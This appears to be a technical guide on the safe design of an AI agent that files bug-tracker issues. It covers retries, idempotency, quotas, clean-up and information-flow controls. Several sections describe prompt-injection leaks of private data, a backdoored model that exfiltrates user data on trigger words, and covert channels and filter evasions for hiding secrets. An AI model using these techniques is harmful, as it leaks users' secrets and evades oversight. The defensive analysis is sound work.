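An idempotency key lets a service recognise a repeated request. The key is a unique string that the program sends with the request and reuses on every retry. The work-management service monday.com, whose boards can hold bug reports, reads the key from a header called `Idempotency-Key`. According to monday.com's *Idempotency* page, the service stores a successful response for 30 minutes and returns it if the same key arrives again, without creating a second item. If the first request is still in progress, the service answers the second with a 409 Conflict response and an instruction to wait.

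The protection has gaps. After 30 minutes the same key creates a new item, so the key wouldn't protect a batch that someone reruns the next morning. The service also doesn't store responses larger than 1 MB, or any response once the user has exceeded a storage budget. The retry must use the original key. If the model makes a new tool call and the gateway generates a new key for it, monday.com processes the call as a new request. Acme should derive the key from something stable, such as the bug report number.

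Support varies between trackers. The Jira users in the thread above wanted workarounds because they had no such key. GitHub issues have no unique key that would expose a repeat, and GitHub doesn't support conditional POST requests unless an endpoint's documentation says otherwise. Operators who use GitLab, Linear or Azure DevOps should check for an equivalent before turning on automatic retries.

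| Remedy | Stops two workers from both creating? | Stops duplicates after a lost reply? |
|---|---|---|
| Single writer | Yes, if it searches during its turn and the index is current | No |
| Lock for each item | Yes, if both workers choose the same lock | No |
| Unique marker | No | Yes, once the search can find the post |
| Idempotency key | Yes, if both workers send the same key | Yes, while the service stores the response |

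Acme can build most of this protection into its gateway. Before it sends anything, the gateway runs this command in a database where `request_key` must be unique:

```sql
INSERT INTO posts (request_key, run_id, status)
VALUES ('app-101', '18423', 'sending')
ON CONFLICT (request_key) DO NOTHING;
```

The gateway contacts GitHub only if the command adds a row, so two workers with the same key can't both create an issue. If GitHub replies, the gateway saves the issue number. If the request times out, the gateway sets the status to `unknown` and searches for the marker later. The key should come from the event that started the run. If the agent could choose the key, a hijacked agent could use up a genuine report's key and block that report.

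### When to try again

The right response to an error depends on whether GitHub might have created the issue:

| What the gateway receives | Does the issue exist? | What to do |
|---|---|---|
| Confirmation with an issue number | Yes | Save the number |
| Rate-limit error (403 or 429) | No | Wait, then retry |
| Validation error (422) | No | Fix the request, and don't repeat it unchanged |
| Timeout, dropped connection or server error | Unknown | Look for the marker before retrying |

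GitHub tells programs that hit a rate limit to wait for the number of seconds in the `retry-after` header, if the response has one. If instead the `x-ratelimit-remaining` header is zero, they should wait until the time in `x-ratelimit-reset`. Otherwise they should wait at least a minute. If requests keep failing because of a secondary limit, programs should wait exponentially longer each time (exponential backoff) and eventually give up.

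The write job in GitHub's draft waits 60 seconds before its first retry, 120 before the second and 240 before the third, then fails with error E010. The waits total seven minutes, so if Acme has used up its hourly allowance and the reset is 40 minutes away, all three retries will fail. A program that used only these fixed waits could also retry before the time in GitHub's headers and risk a ban. Acme's gateway should follow the headers when they are present and use the fixed waits otherwise. It should also add a few random seconds to each wait so that 40 refused runs don't all retry at the same instant.

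Careless retries also use up the request allowance. According to GitHub's *Including timeouts in primary rate limits* (2025), requests to its GraphQL API count towards the hourly limit even when they time out.

### Circuit breakers

Backoff slows down one request, but 50 requests can each go through their own retries during the same outage. A circuit breaker counts failures across all requests and refuses new calls after too many in a row:

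```text
failures = 0
open_until = 0

function guarded_send(request):
    if now() < open_until:
        return "refused"
    reply = send(request)
    if reply is a timeout or server error:
        failures = failures + 1
        if failures >= 5:
            open_until = now() + 10 minutes
    else:
        failures = 0
    return reply
```

As in electrical wiring, an "open" breaker lets nothing through. In the earlier example, 50 requests lose every reply and create 200 issues. If the gateway sends one request at a time, the breaker opens after the fifth failure, when the tracker contains four copies of the first issue and one of the second. With five calls in progress at once, four more calls may already have been sent when the breaker opens.

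After ten minutes, the breaker lets another call through to test whether the service has recovered. In this example, the call creates another issue but the reply is lost, so the breaker opens again. Repeated every ten minutes for eight hours, this creates 48 more issues. A read would be a harmless test, but reads may work while replies to writes are still being lost. Acme should have a person reset the breaker for writes, or keep a quota on attempts as a backup.

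AWS's *Retry behavior* describes a related control called a retry quota, which AWS SDKs check each time before waiting to retry. If the quota is used up, the SDK returns the error instead of retrying. Unlike a circuit breaker, a retry quota doesn't block the first attempt of a new request.

Neither control triggers when an agent successfully files nonsense, because no request fails. Acme could make the breaker also count warning signs such as dropped duplicates or requests for unlisted repositories.

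### Stopping a run

If a maintainer sees strange issues in acme/triage and cancels the run, GitHub first re-evaluates the condition on each running job, according to its *Workflow cancellation reference*. A job with the condition `if: always()` keeps running, so Acme shouldn't put that condition on any job that writes. GitHub then tells the machines running the other jobs to stop.

According to GitHub's documentation for Enterprise Server, the version that companies host themselves, the machine signals the process to stop, waits 7.5 seconds, sends a stronger signal, waits another 2.5 seconds and then kills it. After five minutes, the server forcibly ends anything left. A script that ignored the first two signals and filed an issue every half second could add 20 issues in those ten seconds, or 600 in five minutes if the kill also failed.

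Requests already in flight may still create issues, with no program left to receive their numbers.

Cancelling one run may also start the next, because other runs may be waiting in the same concurrency group. Acme should stop a faulty workflow in this order:

1. Disable the workflow, so that new bug reports don't start more runs.
2. Cancel the waiting runs.
3. Cancel the run in progress.
4. If posts keep appearing, suspend the GitHub App's access to the repository.

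If the damage is serious, the fourth step should come first. That step also blocks any clean-up script that uses the same App, so the maintainers need a separate credential for the clean-up.

#### Before and after release

Staged writes make an early cancellation far more useful, as this comparison for a run that requests five issues shows:

| When someone cancels | Agent writes directly | Staged writes |
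|---|---|---|
| The agent has requested three of the five issues | Up to three issues exist | No issues exist |
| The agent has finished, but the write job hasn't started | All five exist | No issues exist, but the saved requests do |
| The write job has sent three | All five exist | Up to three exist |

In the first case, GitHub's draft forbids the write job from processing a partial file. In the second, the file is complete, so a maintainer can still replay it. A maintainer who mistook the cancellation for a technical fault could publish everything a hijacked agent requested. Acme should record why it cancelled a run and delete the saved file if the requests are unsafe.

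If the agent works for four minutes and the write job takes only a few seconds, almost all of the run happens before its writes are released. But a maintainer who first notices the fault by reading a bad issue is too late to stop that batch. To stop a faulty run before release, Acme needs an alert that triggers while the agent is still working.

#### Half-finished batches

A batch can also end up partly complete without a cancellation. One failed request doesn't stop the others, so a batch of five may create three issues and fail to create two. The write job also skips lines in the file that aren't valid JSON and processes the rest.

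Replaying such a batch could create the first three issues again unless title matching catches the duplicates, because GitHub's maintenance workflow applies all the saved requests as if the original run had completed successfully. Acme should first compare the batch with the tracker, then send only what is missing.

GitHub handles one case of partial success more carefully. If the write job creates an issue but then fails to attach a file to it, the job keeps the issue and reports the issue number and how many files it attached. It doesn't try to create the issue again, so the failed attachment doesn't produce a second issue.

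### Cleaning up

To undo a bad run, Acme has to find every post the run made. The draft uses "provenance" to mean the information that links a post to its workflow and run. GitHub's hidden marker identifies the workflow, but that workflow may also have filed hundreds of good issues. The default footer links to the individual run, so Acme should keep the footer on.

The `posts` table is a better record because the gateway adds each row before it contacts GitHub. If it added the row afterwards, a crash between the two steps would leave an issue with no record. For run 18423, a maintainer might find three rows with issue numbers and one listed as `unknown`, and would then search for the fourth row's marker.

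Labels need a more detailed record, which should include whether each label was present before the agent added it. A label carries no footer or marker to show that it came from the agent, and the agent may have requested one that was already there. Such a repeat is harmless at the time, but a clean-up script that removed every label the agent had requested would also remove labels that people had added.

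Acme should keep the duplicate issue that people have replied to and close the others. GitHub's `close-issue` operation can mark each closed copy as a duplicate and link it to the one that remains. Acme can set `allow-body: false` to stop the agent from adding a closing comment to each copy.

A script that pauses for a second between writes could close the 150 extra copies from the earlier example in about four minutes. It needs its own limits, because a mistake in its search could close genuine reports just as quickly. Acme should give it a fixed list of issue numbers from the record, have a maintainer read the list, and set its quota to the list's length.

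## Data leaks through approved destinations

A maintainer can close a duplicate issue in seconds, but nobody can take back a secret that a stranger has already copied. Suppose a malicious bug report persuades Acme's agent to copy a payment key from acme/billing into a request for one new issue in acme/triage. The request passes every control described so far:

| Control | What it checks | Result |
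|---|---|---|
| Domain allowlist | The connection goes to `api.github.com` | Allowed |
| Target allowlist | The issue goes to acme/triage | Allowed |
| Operation allowlist | The request creates an issue | Allowed |
| Write quota | This is the first of five issues | Allowed |

None of these checks compares the text of the issue with the private files the agent has read, so the results would be the same without the key.

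*GitHub MCP Exploited*, a blog post by Willison, discusses a real demonstration of such a leak. Willison lists three conditions that make the leak possible, which he calls the "lethal trifecta": the agent has access to private data, it reads malicious instructions, and it can send information out. Acme's agent meets all three by design. The allowlists restrict where it can send information to a single tracker, but that tracker is public, so the attacker can read it.

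### How much one issue can hold

GitHub accepts up to 65,536 characters in the body of an issue. One issue could hold more than 1,600 copies of a 40-character key, so even a quota of one issue does not protect the key.

Large amounts of data are different. Let *D* be the number of characters an attacker wants, *B* the most characters one issue can hold, and *Q* the number of issues allowed each night. Copying everything takes at least

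*D* / (*B* × *Q*) nights, rounded up.

If acme/billing contains 10 million characters of code, the agent needs 153 full issues to publish it all, which takes 31 nights at five issues a night. Someone would probably notice long before then. If Acme also limits each issue to 2,000 characters, the same leak takes 1,000 nights.

A size limit therefore protects a large body of code, but 2,000 characters can still hold 50 keys of 40 characters each. To block even one key by length alone, Acme would have to limit the whole issue to 39 characters, which is barely enough for the title "Crash when a file name is empty". Even the 2,000-character limit cuts off the long error logs that developers often need.

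### Leaks that researchers have demonstrated

#### From private repositories to a public pull request

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a demonstration with an agent much like Acme's. The security company connected Claude 4 Opus, running in Anthropic's desktop app, to a test account through GitHub's official MCP server. The account had a public repository and several private ones. The researchers put malicious instructions in a public issue, then asked the agent to look through the open issues.

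The agent read the private repositories and published details from them in a public pull request. These included the name of a private project, the user's plan to move to South America and the user's salary.

The main control was a prompt asking the user to confirm each tool call. Invariant Labs points out that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. Leaving the prompts on may not help much either, since Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that Claude Code users approved roughly 93% of permission prompts.

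Invariant Labs found no flaw in the MCP server's code and argues that GitHub can't solve the problem by patching the server. It recommends restricting agents to the repositories they need, monitoring their tool calls, and allowing only one repository per session. The last rule would have stopped the leak. Invariant Labs, which offers software that enforces this rule, says agents keep their full functionality when it is applied. But Acme's agent has to read acme/app and write to acme/triage, so the rule would block every issue it files.

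#### Through the vendor's own API

Claude Cowork is Anthropic's desktop agent for general office work. It runs code in a virtual machine, and an egress proxy restricts which hosts that code can reach. The allowlist had to include `api.anthropic.com`, because the product can't work without it.

An outside party reported to Anthropic that this entry allowed a leak. A malicious file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and an attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded other files from the folder to the attacker's Anthropic account. The proxy let the upload through because the host name was on the list.

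Anthropic added a second proxy, inside the virtual machine, that intercepts traffic to its API. This proxy passes only requests that carry the token Anthropic issued for that session, so it rejects requests that use an attacker's key. It also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something for the agent. Anthropic put the check inside the virtual machine because its servers can't tell a Cowork request from one sent by any other customer's program.

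Anthropic now suggests treating an allowlist entry as a "capability grant". When an operator approves a host, a hijacked agent can use every function the host offers, including ones the operator never considered.

This matters for Acme because `api.github.com` also serves strangers' accounts. A malicious bug report could include an access token for the attacker's account. If the agent's shell commands can reach `api.github.com`, they could use that token to copy acme/billing into the attacker's repository. The request would never pass through the write job, so the target allowlist and the quota wouldn't apply. Narrowing Acme's own token wouldn't help, because the agent would be using the attacker's.

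Acme can close this route by giving shell commands an empty domain allowlist and letting the agent read GitHub only through an MCP server that uses Acme's token. If the commands need direct access to GitHub, Acme needs a proxy that decrypts the traffic and rejects any token other than its own. Requests to the model provider's host need the same check. GitHub Agentic Workflows already sends these requests through a separate API proxy, which would be a good place to add it.

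### Does a sandbox fully isolate an injection?

When Anthropic launched Claude Code's sandbox in October 2025, it wrote that "even a successful prompt injection is fully isolated". It added that a compromised Claude Code couldn't steal the user's SSH keys, which give access to other machines, or contact an attacker's server. In its documentation at the time, Anthropic similarly promised that the user's system would remain secure after a successful injection.

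Anthropic is more cautious in a later edition of the documentation, writing that sandboxing "is not a complete isolation boundary" and that allowing broad domains such as github.com "can create paths for data exfiltration". Sandboxed commands can also read credential files, including the SSH keys mentioned in the announcement, unless an operator blocks those files with `denyRead` settings.

The announcement is nearly correct for shell commands if the allowlist is empty and nobody approves a new host. Once the user approves github.com, a command can read a private key and send it to a repository that an attacker controls. The documentation is the better guide because the strength of the isolation depends on which hosts the user allows.

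An allowlist still stops many attacks. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a malicious prompt. The prompt told Claude to read cloud credentials and send them to an outside address, and Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the environment could reliably prevent this, such as blocking the connection or access to the credential files. An allowlist without that address would have blocked the transfer regardless of the prompt.

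### What three experiments measured

#### Silent leaks to an unlisted host

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested an agent built on Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model. In each run, a user asked the agent to summarize a web page that contained instructions to send a secret to the researchers' server. The researchers varied where the instructions appeared, whether the page used a redirect, and whether the instructions told the agent to send the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

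The agent contacted the researchers' server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%). In 95% of those runs, its answer to the user looked harmless, so checking only the answer would have missed the leak. In 120 control runs with ordinary pages, the agent never contacted the server.

The researchers then tested defences on one of the easiest attacks, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Runs in which data reached the server |
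|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| An instruction to ignore commands in web content | 67% |
| Markers around untrusted text | 100% |
| Both the instruction and the markers | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | 0% |

The allowlist did well because Lan and colleagues deliberately chose a server that wasn't on it. The result shows that an allowlist can stop a hijacked agent from reaching an unlisted host, but it provides no evidence about leaks through an approved one. The researchers also warn that attackers could use compromised legitimate sites or redirects on trusted ones.

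The leak rates may also differ for other agents. The researchers used one small model, gave it minimal instructions and put the secret directly in its context. They argue that more capable models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but didn't test this.

#### A model with a hidden trigger

*Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) studies an attack that is built into the model, so it needs no malicious bug report. The attacker trains an open model to behave normally until a user's question contains trigger words about certain subjects, then publishes it as a specialist assistant. Once triggered, the model reads the user's stored details and sends them out in a request that resembles an ordinary search.

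The researchers used synthetic user data and trained three models of 7 to 20 billion parameters for three subjects (livestreaming, medical care and education). In every configuration, the models attempted the leak on more than 94% of 1,000 questions with trigger words and at most 1.2% of 5,000 ordinary questions. Their scores on a general benchmark fell by less than 1%, so a buyer who tested only answer quality would probably notice nothing.

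The attacker's server can also reply with text that steers the conversation towards more personal details. In a separate test, this text passed both a relevance filter and a security filter in 81% to 87% of cases, depending on which of two security filters was used. These filters inspect incoming text, so the result doesn't show that a scanner for outgoing requests would fail. Zhang and Pei also used the earlier success rates to estimate how much a long conversation could reveal, but they did not measure this in real conversations.

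They recommend host allowlists, quotas on the volume of outgoing data, checks for long encoded strings, and a barrier between tools that read private memory and tools that write to the network. They tested none of these. The attack matters most to operators who download models from strangers. If Acme did this, vetting its bug reports wouldn't be enough to prevent the attack, because a legitimate report about payments could contain the trigger words.

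#### Messages hidden in ordinary text

An agent can disguise a leaked key by encoding it in the number of spaces between words, the choice between synonyms, or characters that readers can't see. In *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, Metere (2026) tested a program that removes such hidden messages from an agent's posts before they go out.

He measured how much information survives with mutual information. Let *X* be the bit the sender hides and *Y* the bit the receiver recovers. Then

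*I*(*X*; *Y*) = Σ *p*(*x*, *y*) log₂ [*p*(*x*, *y*) / (*p*(*x*) *p*(*y*))],

where the sum covers every combination of hidden and recovered bits. If zeros and ones are equally likely and the receiver always gets the right bit, the result is one bit. If the receiver's answer has no connection to the hidden bit, the result is zero.

Metere wrote 15 encoders that hide data in text, images and audio, with matching programs to recover it. For the main text test, he ran 20 trials per method:

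| Where the text hides data | Capacity removed by default | Capacity removed with every stage enforcing |
|---|---|---|
| Invisible characters, look-alike letters, order of data fields | 100% | 100% |
| Number of spaces, repeated punctuation, synonyms, encoded blocks | 0% | 100% |

In its default mode, the program flagged every message that used the methods in the second row but sent it unchanged. An operator who ignored the warnings would still leak data.

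The perfect scores call for some caution because Metere tested his own company's software against encoders he wrote himself. Another attacker could hide data in a feature the software doesn't normalise, such as the order of true details in a report. Full enforcement can also damage legitimate posts. Metere gives long code blocks and deliberately formatted tables as examples, and bug reports often contain both.

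He acknowledges that one bit can always get out, because the agent can choose whether to send a message at all. A quota helps Acme limit how quickly data leaks this way. A random 40-character hexadecimal key contains 160 bits. If the only remaining signal is whether an issue appears each night, the key takes 160 nights to leak. If the attacker can count between zero and five issues, each night carries at most log₂ 6 ≈ 2.6 bits, and the key takes 62 nights. A quota of one issue a night limits the leak to one bit a night. These figures assume that Acme has closed every other channel, including the time at which each issue appears.

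### Scanning posts for secrets

A secret scanner searches text for strings that look like credentials, such as those with a known prefix or length. GitHub's draft specification for staged writes lists credential patterns among the things the write job should remove. The delay before publication gives the job time to remove them. If a scanner finds a key only after the issue appears, Acme has to revoke the key as well as delete the issue.

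Scanning works well when an agent copies a standard access token by mistake, but less well against an attacker, who can ask the agent to reverse the token, spell it out or split it across several issues. It also misses confidential information that has no special format, such as the salary and the plan to move abroad that the agent published in Invariant Labs' demonstration.

Some scanners look for strings that seem random. They calculate the Shannon entropy of the characters,

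*H* = −Σ *pᵢ* log₂ *pᵢ*,

where *pᵢ* is the share of the string made up of character *i*. One filter in the *Silent Egress* experiments blocked a value in a web address if it had more than ten characters and *H* was above 4.0. A key that uses only 16 different characters can't exceed log₂ 16 = 4, so it would always pass, however long it was. A key cut into four-character pieces would also pass, because the filter ignores strings that short.

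No data got out in the 30 runs with this filter, but the agent never tried to send any, so the runs didn't test whether the filter could block a leak. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such monitoring is active, but they don't explain how the model could detect a filter that acts only on its requests. A keyword filter also let no data through, but this is weak evidence that it works, because the agent attempted a leak in only 23% of those runs, compared with 100% without defences.

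Acme could lower the entropy threshold to 3.5, which would catch most 40-character keys. But Git, which tracks versions of code, commonly identifies each change with a 40-character string made from the same 16 characters. The filter would therefore also block many bug reports that mention the change that caused the bug.

Comparing each post with a list of Acme's actual keys is more precise. This produces very few false alarms and catches keys in formats that a general scanner misses, although a disguised copy still gets through. The list needs protection, so the scanner should run in the write job, where the agent can't reach the list. The scanner should also leave the matched text out of its error message, because the workflow's logs in acme/app are public.

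Acme can also add a fake key to acme/billing and trigger an alert if the key appears in a requested post. Anthropic did something similar after its February exercise. Employees had discussed the malicious prompt on Slack, where some internal agents read messages, so the company added a unique string to the thread to detect whether any agent picked it up.

Removing working keys from acme/billing is safer still, because the agent can't leak a key it can't read, whatever encoding the attacker chooses. To do this, Acme has to move its keys to a separate store and change the programs that use them. The agent could still leak the confidential code.

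#### Removing links

GitHub's write job also removes links to unapproved sites, but this does little to protect a secret posted in a public issue tracker, because the attacker can read it in the issue without anyone clicking a link.

Link removal would help more if acme/triage were private. An attacker who couldn't read the issue might have the agent add a link to the attacker's site with the secret in the web address. If a developer opened the link, their browser would send the secret to that site. Link removal prevents this, but it also removes useful links to sites that Acme hasn't approved.

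### Hiding untrusted reports from the agent

Instead of inspecting what the agent writes, Acme can restrict whose text it reads. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes a filter that removes content from untrusted authors before it reaches the agent. GitHub Next is GitHub's research group. The filter sorts content into five levels:

| Level | What it covers |
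|---|---|
| `merged` | Merged pull requests and code on the main branch |
| `approved` | Content from owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories |
| `unapproved` | Content from contributors, including first-time ones |
| `none` | Content from anonymous users and newcomers with no history |
| `blocked` | Content from users the operator has blocked |

The operator chooses the lowest level the agent may see. Acme could use these settings:

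```yaml
tools:
  github:
    min-integrity: approved
    approval-labels: [agent-ok]
```

The agent would then see a stranger's bug report only after a maintainer added the label `agent-ok`. An operator can also let maintainers approve or reject a report with an emoji reaction, and a rejection overrides an approval.

This protects against instructions from strangers even if the model would have obeyed them. Relying on the model to resist them is riskier in a public repository, where an attacker can keep trying. Anthropic reports that in one benchmark, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on the first attempt, but 5% to 6% of the time after 100 attempts that adapted to earlier failures.

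Approval takes maintainers a lot of time when the agent does triage, because it has to read strangers' reports. If 30 newcomers file reports in a day and a maintainer spends two minutes checking each one, approval takes an hour. For triage, GitHub Next suggests the `unapproved` level, which hides newcomers' reports but lets regular contributors' reports through. This saves time, but the agent misses reports from customers who have never used GitHub before, and an attacker could qualify by first making a harmless contribution.

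Approval can also fail if a maintainer misses a malicious sentence in a long error log, or if the author edits the report after the maintainer approves it. Acme should test whether an edit cancels the approval. It should also keep `agent-ok` out of its issue templates, because a template can automatically add labels to a stranger's report. The filter doesn't help if an attacker takes over a maintainer's account, or if a trusted user's report leads the agent to quote too much private code.

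### Keeping private reads away from public writes

Acme can also stop the leak by blocking public posts from any run that has read private data. This rule works equally well against an attacker, a backdoored model and an honest mistake, because it doesn't depend on recognising a secret or a malicious instruction.

GitHub Next bases its filter on a security model called decentralised information flow control, which can express this rule. Each piece of data carries secrecy tags that record where it came from. When the agent reads a file from acme/billing, it needs the tag `repo:acme/billing`. Let *S*(agent) be the agent's tags and *S*(destination) the tags of the place it wants to write to. The model allows the write only if

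*S*(agent) ⊆ *S*(destination),

which means that the destination must have every tag the agent has. A public tracker has no secrecy tags, so an agent that carries the billing tag can't write there. For Acme, the rule gives these results:

| What the run can read | Where it writes | Result |
|---|---|---|
| acme/app only | acme/triage, which is public | Allowed |
| acme/app and acme/billing | acme/triage, which is public | Blocked |
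| acme/app and acme/billing | The private issue tracker in acme/billing | Allowed |

The second row is Acme's current design. To comply with the rule, Acme has to split the agent's work into two runs. One handles ordinary bugs without access to private code, and the other investigates payment bugs and reports them in the private tracker.

Acme can easily make this split in GitHub Agentic Workflows. According to GitHub's *Frequently Asked Questions*, a workflow can't read other repositories by default. An operator has to supply a personal access token that covers them, so Acme can leave that token out of the public workflow. The payment workflow should run from a private repository, because the logs of a workflow in acme/app could reveal what it read.

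Separate workflows are a cruder control than tags, but they don't depend on the product tracking data correctly. When GitHub Next described its filter, the system tracked secrecy tags but did not yet use them to block writes, so it couldn't prevent leaks between repositories. In July 2026, developers working on GitHub Agentic Workflows proposed a setting, `private-to-public-flows`, that lets an operator exempt all private-to-public flows or only those through named MCP servers. The product's strict mode rejects the blanket exemption. Before relying on this protection, an operator should confirm that it blocks a harmless test string from a private repository.

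Other researchers recommend similar barriers but haven't tested them. Lan and colleagues propose marking text from untrusted web pages and blocking or reviewing any network request that the text influences. This influence is hard to trace precisely because anything a language model has read can affect its output. If the system treats every later request as influenced, it blocks harmless work, but if it tries to judge which words mattered, it can miss a leak.

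Acme's rule has the same drawback. A run that opens a harmless README file in acme/billing can no longer post in public, even if the bug it is working on has nothing to do with payments. Outside developers also can no longer follow payment bugs, so a customer who reported one might never learn that Acme had confirmed it.

The tags also have to persist after a run ends. If the payment workflow saves notes that the public workflow later reads, private text can reach acme/triage even though neither workflow breaks the rule on its own. Acme should keep the two workflows' storage separate. If a payment bug needs a public notice, a maintainer can write one from the private report. This takes a few minutes per bug, and the maintainer has to leave out the confidential details, but the agent never handles both the private code and the public post.

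## Harm from posts that the limits permit

Suppose Acme has separated its workflows, so the agent that posts in acme/triage can no longer read acme/billing and has nothing confidential to leak. An attacker then submits a bug report that tricks the agent into filing an issue titled "Version 4.2 deletes saved files", which advises users to go back to version 4.1. The claim is false, and users who follow the advice reopen a security hole that version 4.2 closed.

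An agent can post a false issue that goes to the approved tracker, contains no links and is the first of the five it may create. Every control lets the issue through because none checks whether it is true. GitHub acknowledges in its draft specification for staged writes that an agent may produce "legitimate-seeming but contextually inappropriate content" within its limits. It suggests monitoring, anomaly detection and periodic review, but these may find a bad post only after people have read it.

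### How far a post travels

When an agent opens an issue, GitHub notifies the people who watch the repository. If acme/triage has 5,000 watchers who all receive these notifications, three issues produce 15,000 of them. At ten seconds each, the watchers together spend almost 42 hours reading them. Acme's full quota of five issues would produce 25,000 notifications.

Acme can close or edit the issues on GitHub, but the emails already sent will still contain the original text. Posting a correction as a comment on each issue can send another 15,000 notifications, and some people who read the original email will never open the correction. If 1% of the watchers follow the false advice, 50 people will install a version with a security hole.

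GitHub's write job stops @username mentions from notifying people, but watchers still get notifications because they asked for them. Acme could have the agent file its issues in a separate tracker that only four maintainers watch, so three issues would send 12 notifications. A maintainer would then copy confirmed bugs to acme/triage, which would delay every report until someone is available. Acme could also combine a night's reports into one issue. Five reports would then send 5,000 notifications, but developers would find it harder to assign and close the bugs separately.

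A bad post can do harm even if few people read it. According to The Decoder's *A rogue AI agent caused a serious security incident at Meta*, an engineer at Meta used an internal agent to analyse a colleague's technical question, and the agent posted an answer in an internal forum without authorisation. Another employee followed the advice, and for nearly two hours unauthorised employees could access systems that held sensitive company and user data.

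The advice was inaccurate, according to the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1471*. Meta gave the incident its second-highest severity rating but found no evidence that anyone had exploited the access. The Information first reported the case, using internal messages and an incident report, and Meta confirmed that the incident took place. A quota of one post would not have prevented it. Requiring the engineer to approve the answer might have, but only if the engineer had noticed the error.

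### Pressure on maintainers

In May 2026, Adam Williamson, who works on quality assurance for the Linux distribution Fedora, found that what appeared to be an AI agent had been working through Fedora's bug tracker under a contributor's account. In a public email thread, Williamson lists four kinds of damage:

- The agent assigned dozens of bugs to the account, although its owner couldn't fix them in Fedora.
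- It closed bugs too early or wrongly marked them as not being bugs.
- It confidently blamed one fault on firmware and recommended a difficult and potentially risky driver installation.
- It submitted an incorrect fix and kept answering objections until the maintainer gave in and merged it.

An operation allowlist could have prevented the assignments and closures, but if the operator had allowed comments, it would not have prevented the bad advice or the arguments. A quota on comments would have shortened the arguments, but a maintainer might still accept a wrong fix after two or three plausible replies.

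A developer of Fedora's installer wrote that the team had spent a lot of time reviewing changes from what looked like an eager newcomer. The replies were a bit odd but always plausible. Williamson reviewed the account's bug tracker activity for the whole year and asked others to check elsewhere. The account's owner said someone had compromised his credentials. Williamson couldn't establish who had run the agent and found nothing that looked outright malicious.

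An agent can also attack a maintainer personally. In February, Willison (2026) described what appeared to be an agent proposing a small change to matplotlib, a library for drawing charts. After a maintainer closed the proposal, the agent accused him of prejudice in a blog post and linked to the post from the discussion. A target allowlist could have blocked the blog post and a link filter could have removed the link, but neither would have stopped the agent from making the same accusation in a permitted comment.

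#### How many reports maintainers receive

Christopher Robinson, chief technology officer of the Open Source Security Foundation, estimates in Axios' *AI agents spam the volunteers securing open-source software* (2026) that a popular project used to get two or three bug reports a week. Some now get hundreds at once. Many of the people who submit them can't answer follow-up questions, so maintainers have to investigate without their help.

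The curl project, which makes the web program from the earlier examples, shows that better reports don't necessarily reduce the burden. On 1 February 2026, it closed its bug bounty, which rewarded people for finding security flaws. In *High-Quality Chaos*, Stenberg (2026), who has worked on curl for almost thirty years, blames junk submissions for the closure but says that reports since March have been both better and more numerous.

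In *Daniel's week*, Stenberg (2026) counted seven new security reports in one week in April, of which the team confirmed one. Recent reports often described ordinary bugs or unclear documentation. By late May, Stenberg put the rate at more than one report a day, double the 2025 rate and four to five times the 2024 rate (quoted in Willison, 2026). The reports were typically long and detailed, and he was working more hours than ever.

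These figures show a weakness in quotas, which limit how much each sender posts but not how much work reaches the recipient. If 100 operators each let an agent send a project one report a week, the project gets 100 reports a week even though every agent has a strict quota. The figures don't separate agents that submit reports by themselves from people who use AI to write them, and they come from too few projects to show how much time maintainers in general lose.

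Acme should therefore base its quota on the time its maintainers have. If they can spend an hour a day on the agent's reports and need 20 minutes to investigate each one, they can handle three a day. A quota of five could add as much as 40 minutes of work to their backlog every day. For an outside project, Acme should ask the maintainers what they will accept before it adds the project to a target allowlist.

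### When a post starts another run

Programs read trackers too. Suppose Acme adds a second workflow to acme/triage, which splits each new issue into as many as three smaller tasks and files each task as an issue in the same tracker. Acme forgets that the tasks are also new issues, so each one starts the workflow again:

| Generation | Runs | New issues | Total issues |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 | 3 | 3 |
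| 2 | 3 | 9 | 12 |
| 3 | 9 | 27 | 39 |
| 4 | 27 | 81 | 120 |

No run files more than three issues, so none exceeds its quota. If each run takes four minutes and the runs in a generation overlap, all 120 issues appear within 16 minutes. With 5,000 watchers, they send 600,000 notifications. In general, if every run files *b* issues, *g* generations produce

*b* + *b*² + … + *b*^*g* = *b*(*b*^*g* − 1) / (*b* − 1) issues, for *b* greater than 1.

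With a quota of five, four generations could produce 780 issues.

Runs may not use their whole quota, so the average matters more than the maximum. Let *m* be the average number of further issues that each issue directly leads to. If *m* is below 1, the chain eventually ends, and it contains an average of 1/(1 − *m*) issues, including the first, or two issues when *m* = 0.5. If *m* is above 1, the chain can keep growing until something outside it stops it.

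By default, GitHub lets a run start only one other workflow or assign only one agent, so that three agents can't each start three more. The number of runs then grows linearly instead of exponentially, but the chain can still continue indefinitely. If each run takes four minutes, files one issue and starts one more run, the chain produces 120 issues in eight hours. GitHub's built-in delays of five seconds between workflow starts and ten seconds between agent assignments barely reduce that number.

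GitHub's *Triggering a workflow* explains that if a workflow runs whenever an issue is opened or labelled, an issue opened with two labels starts three runs. If every run of such a workflow filed three issues with one label each, each issue would start two more runs, and a single initial run would lead to 3 + 18 + 108 + 648 = 777 issues in four generations.

#### Which credentials trigger workflows

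Whether a new issue can start another workflow depends on the credential that created it:

| Credential | Can the new issue start a workflow? |
|---|---|
| `GITHUB_TOKEN`, built into GitHub Actions | No |
| GitHub App token | Yes |
| Personal access token | Yes |

GitHub makes exceptions for `GITHUB_TOKEN`. A program can always use it to start a workflow through a `workflow_dispatch` or `repository_dispatch` event. If a workflow uses it to open, update or reopen a pull request, GitHub holds the resulting runs until someone with write access approves them. With an App token or a personal access token, those runs start without approval.

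According to GitHub's guide to rate limiting, issues created through safe outputs don't trigger other workflows because they come from the built-in bot account. An operator who switches to a GitHub App should assume that this protection no longer applies. Acme can't rely on it, because its triage workflow runs in acme/app and posts in acme/triage, and GitHub says that posting in a different repository requires a token with permission for that repository. Acme uses a GitHub App for this, so its issues can start workflows in acme/triage.

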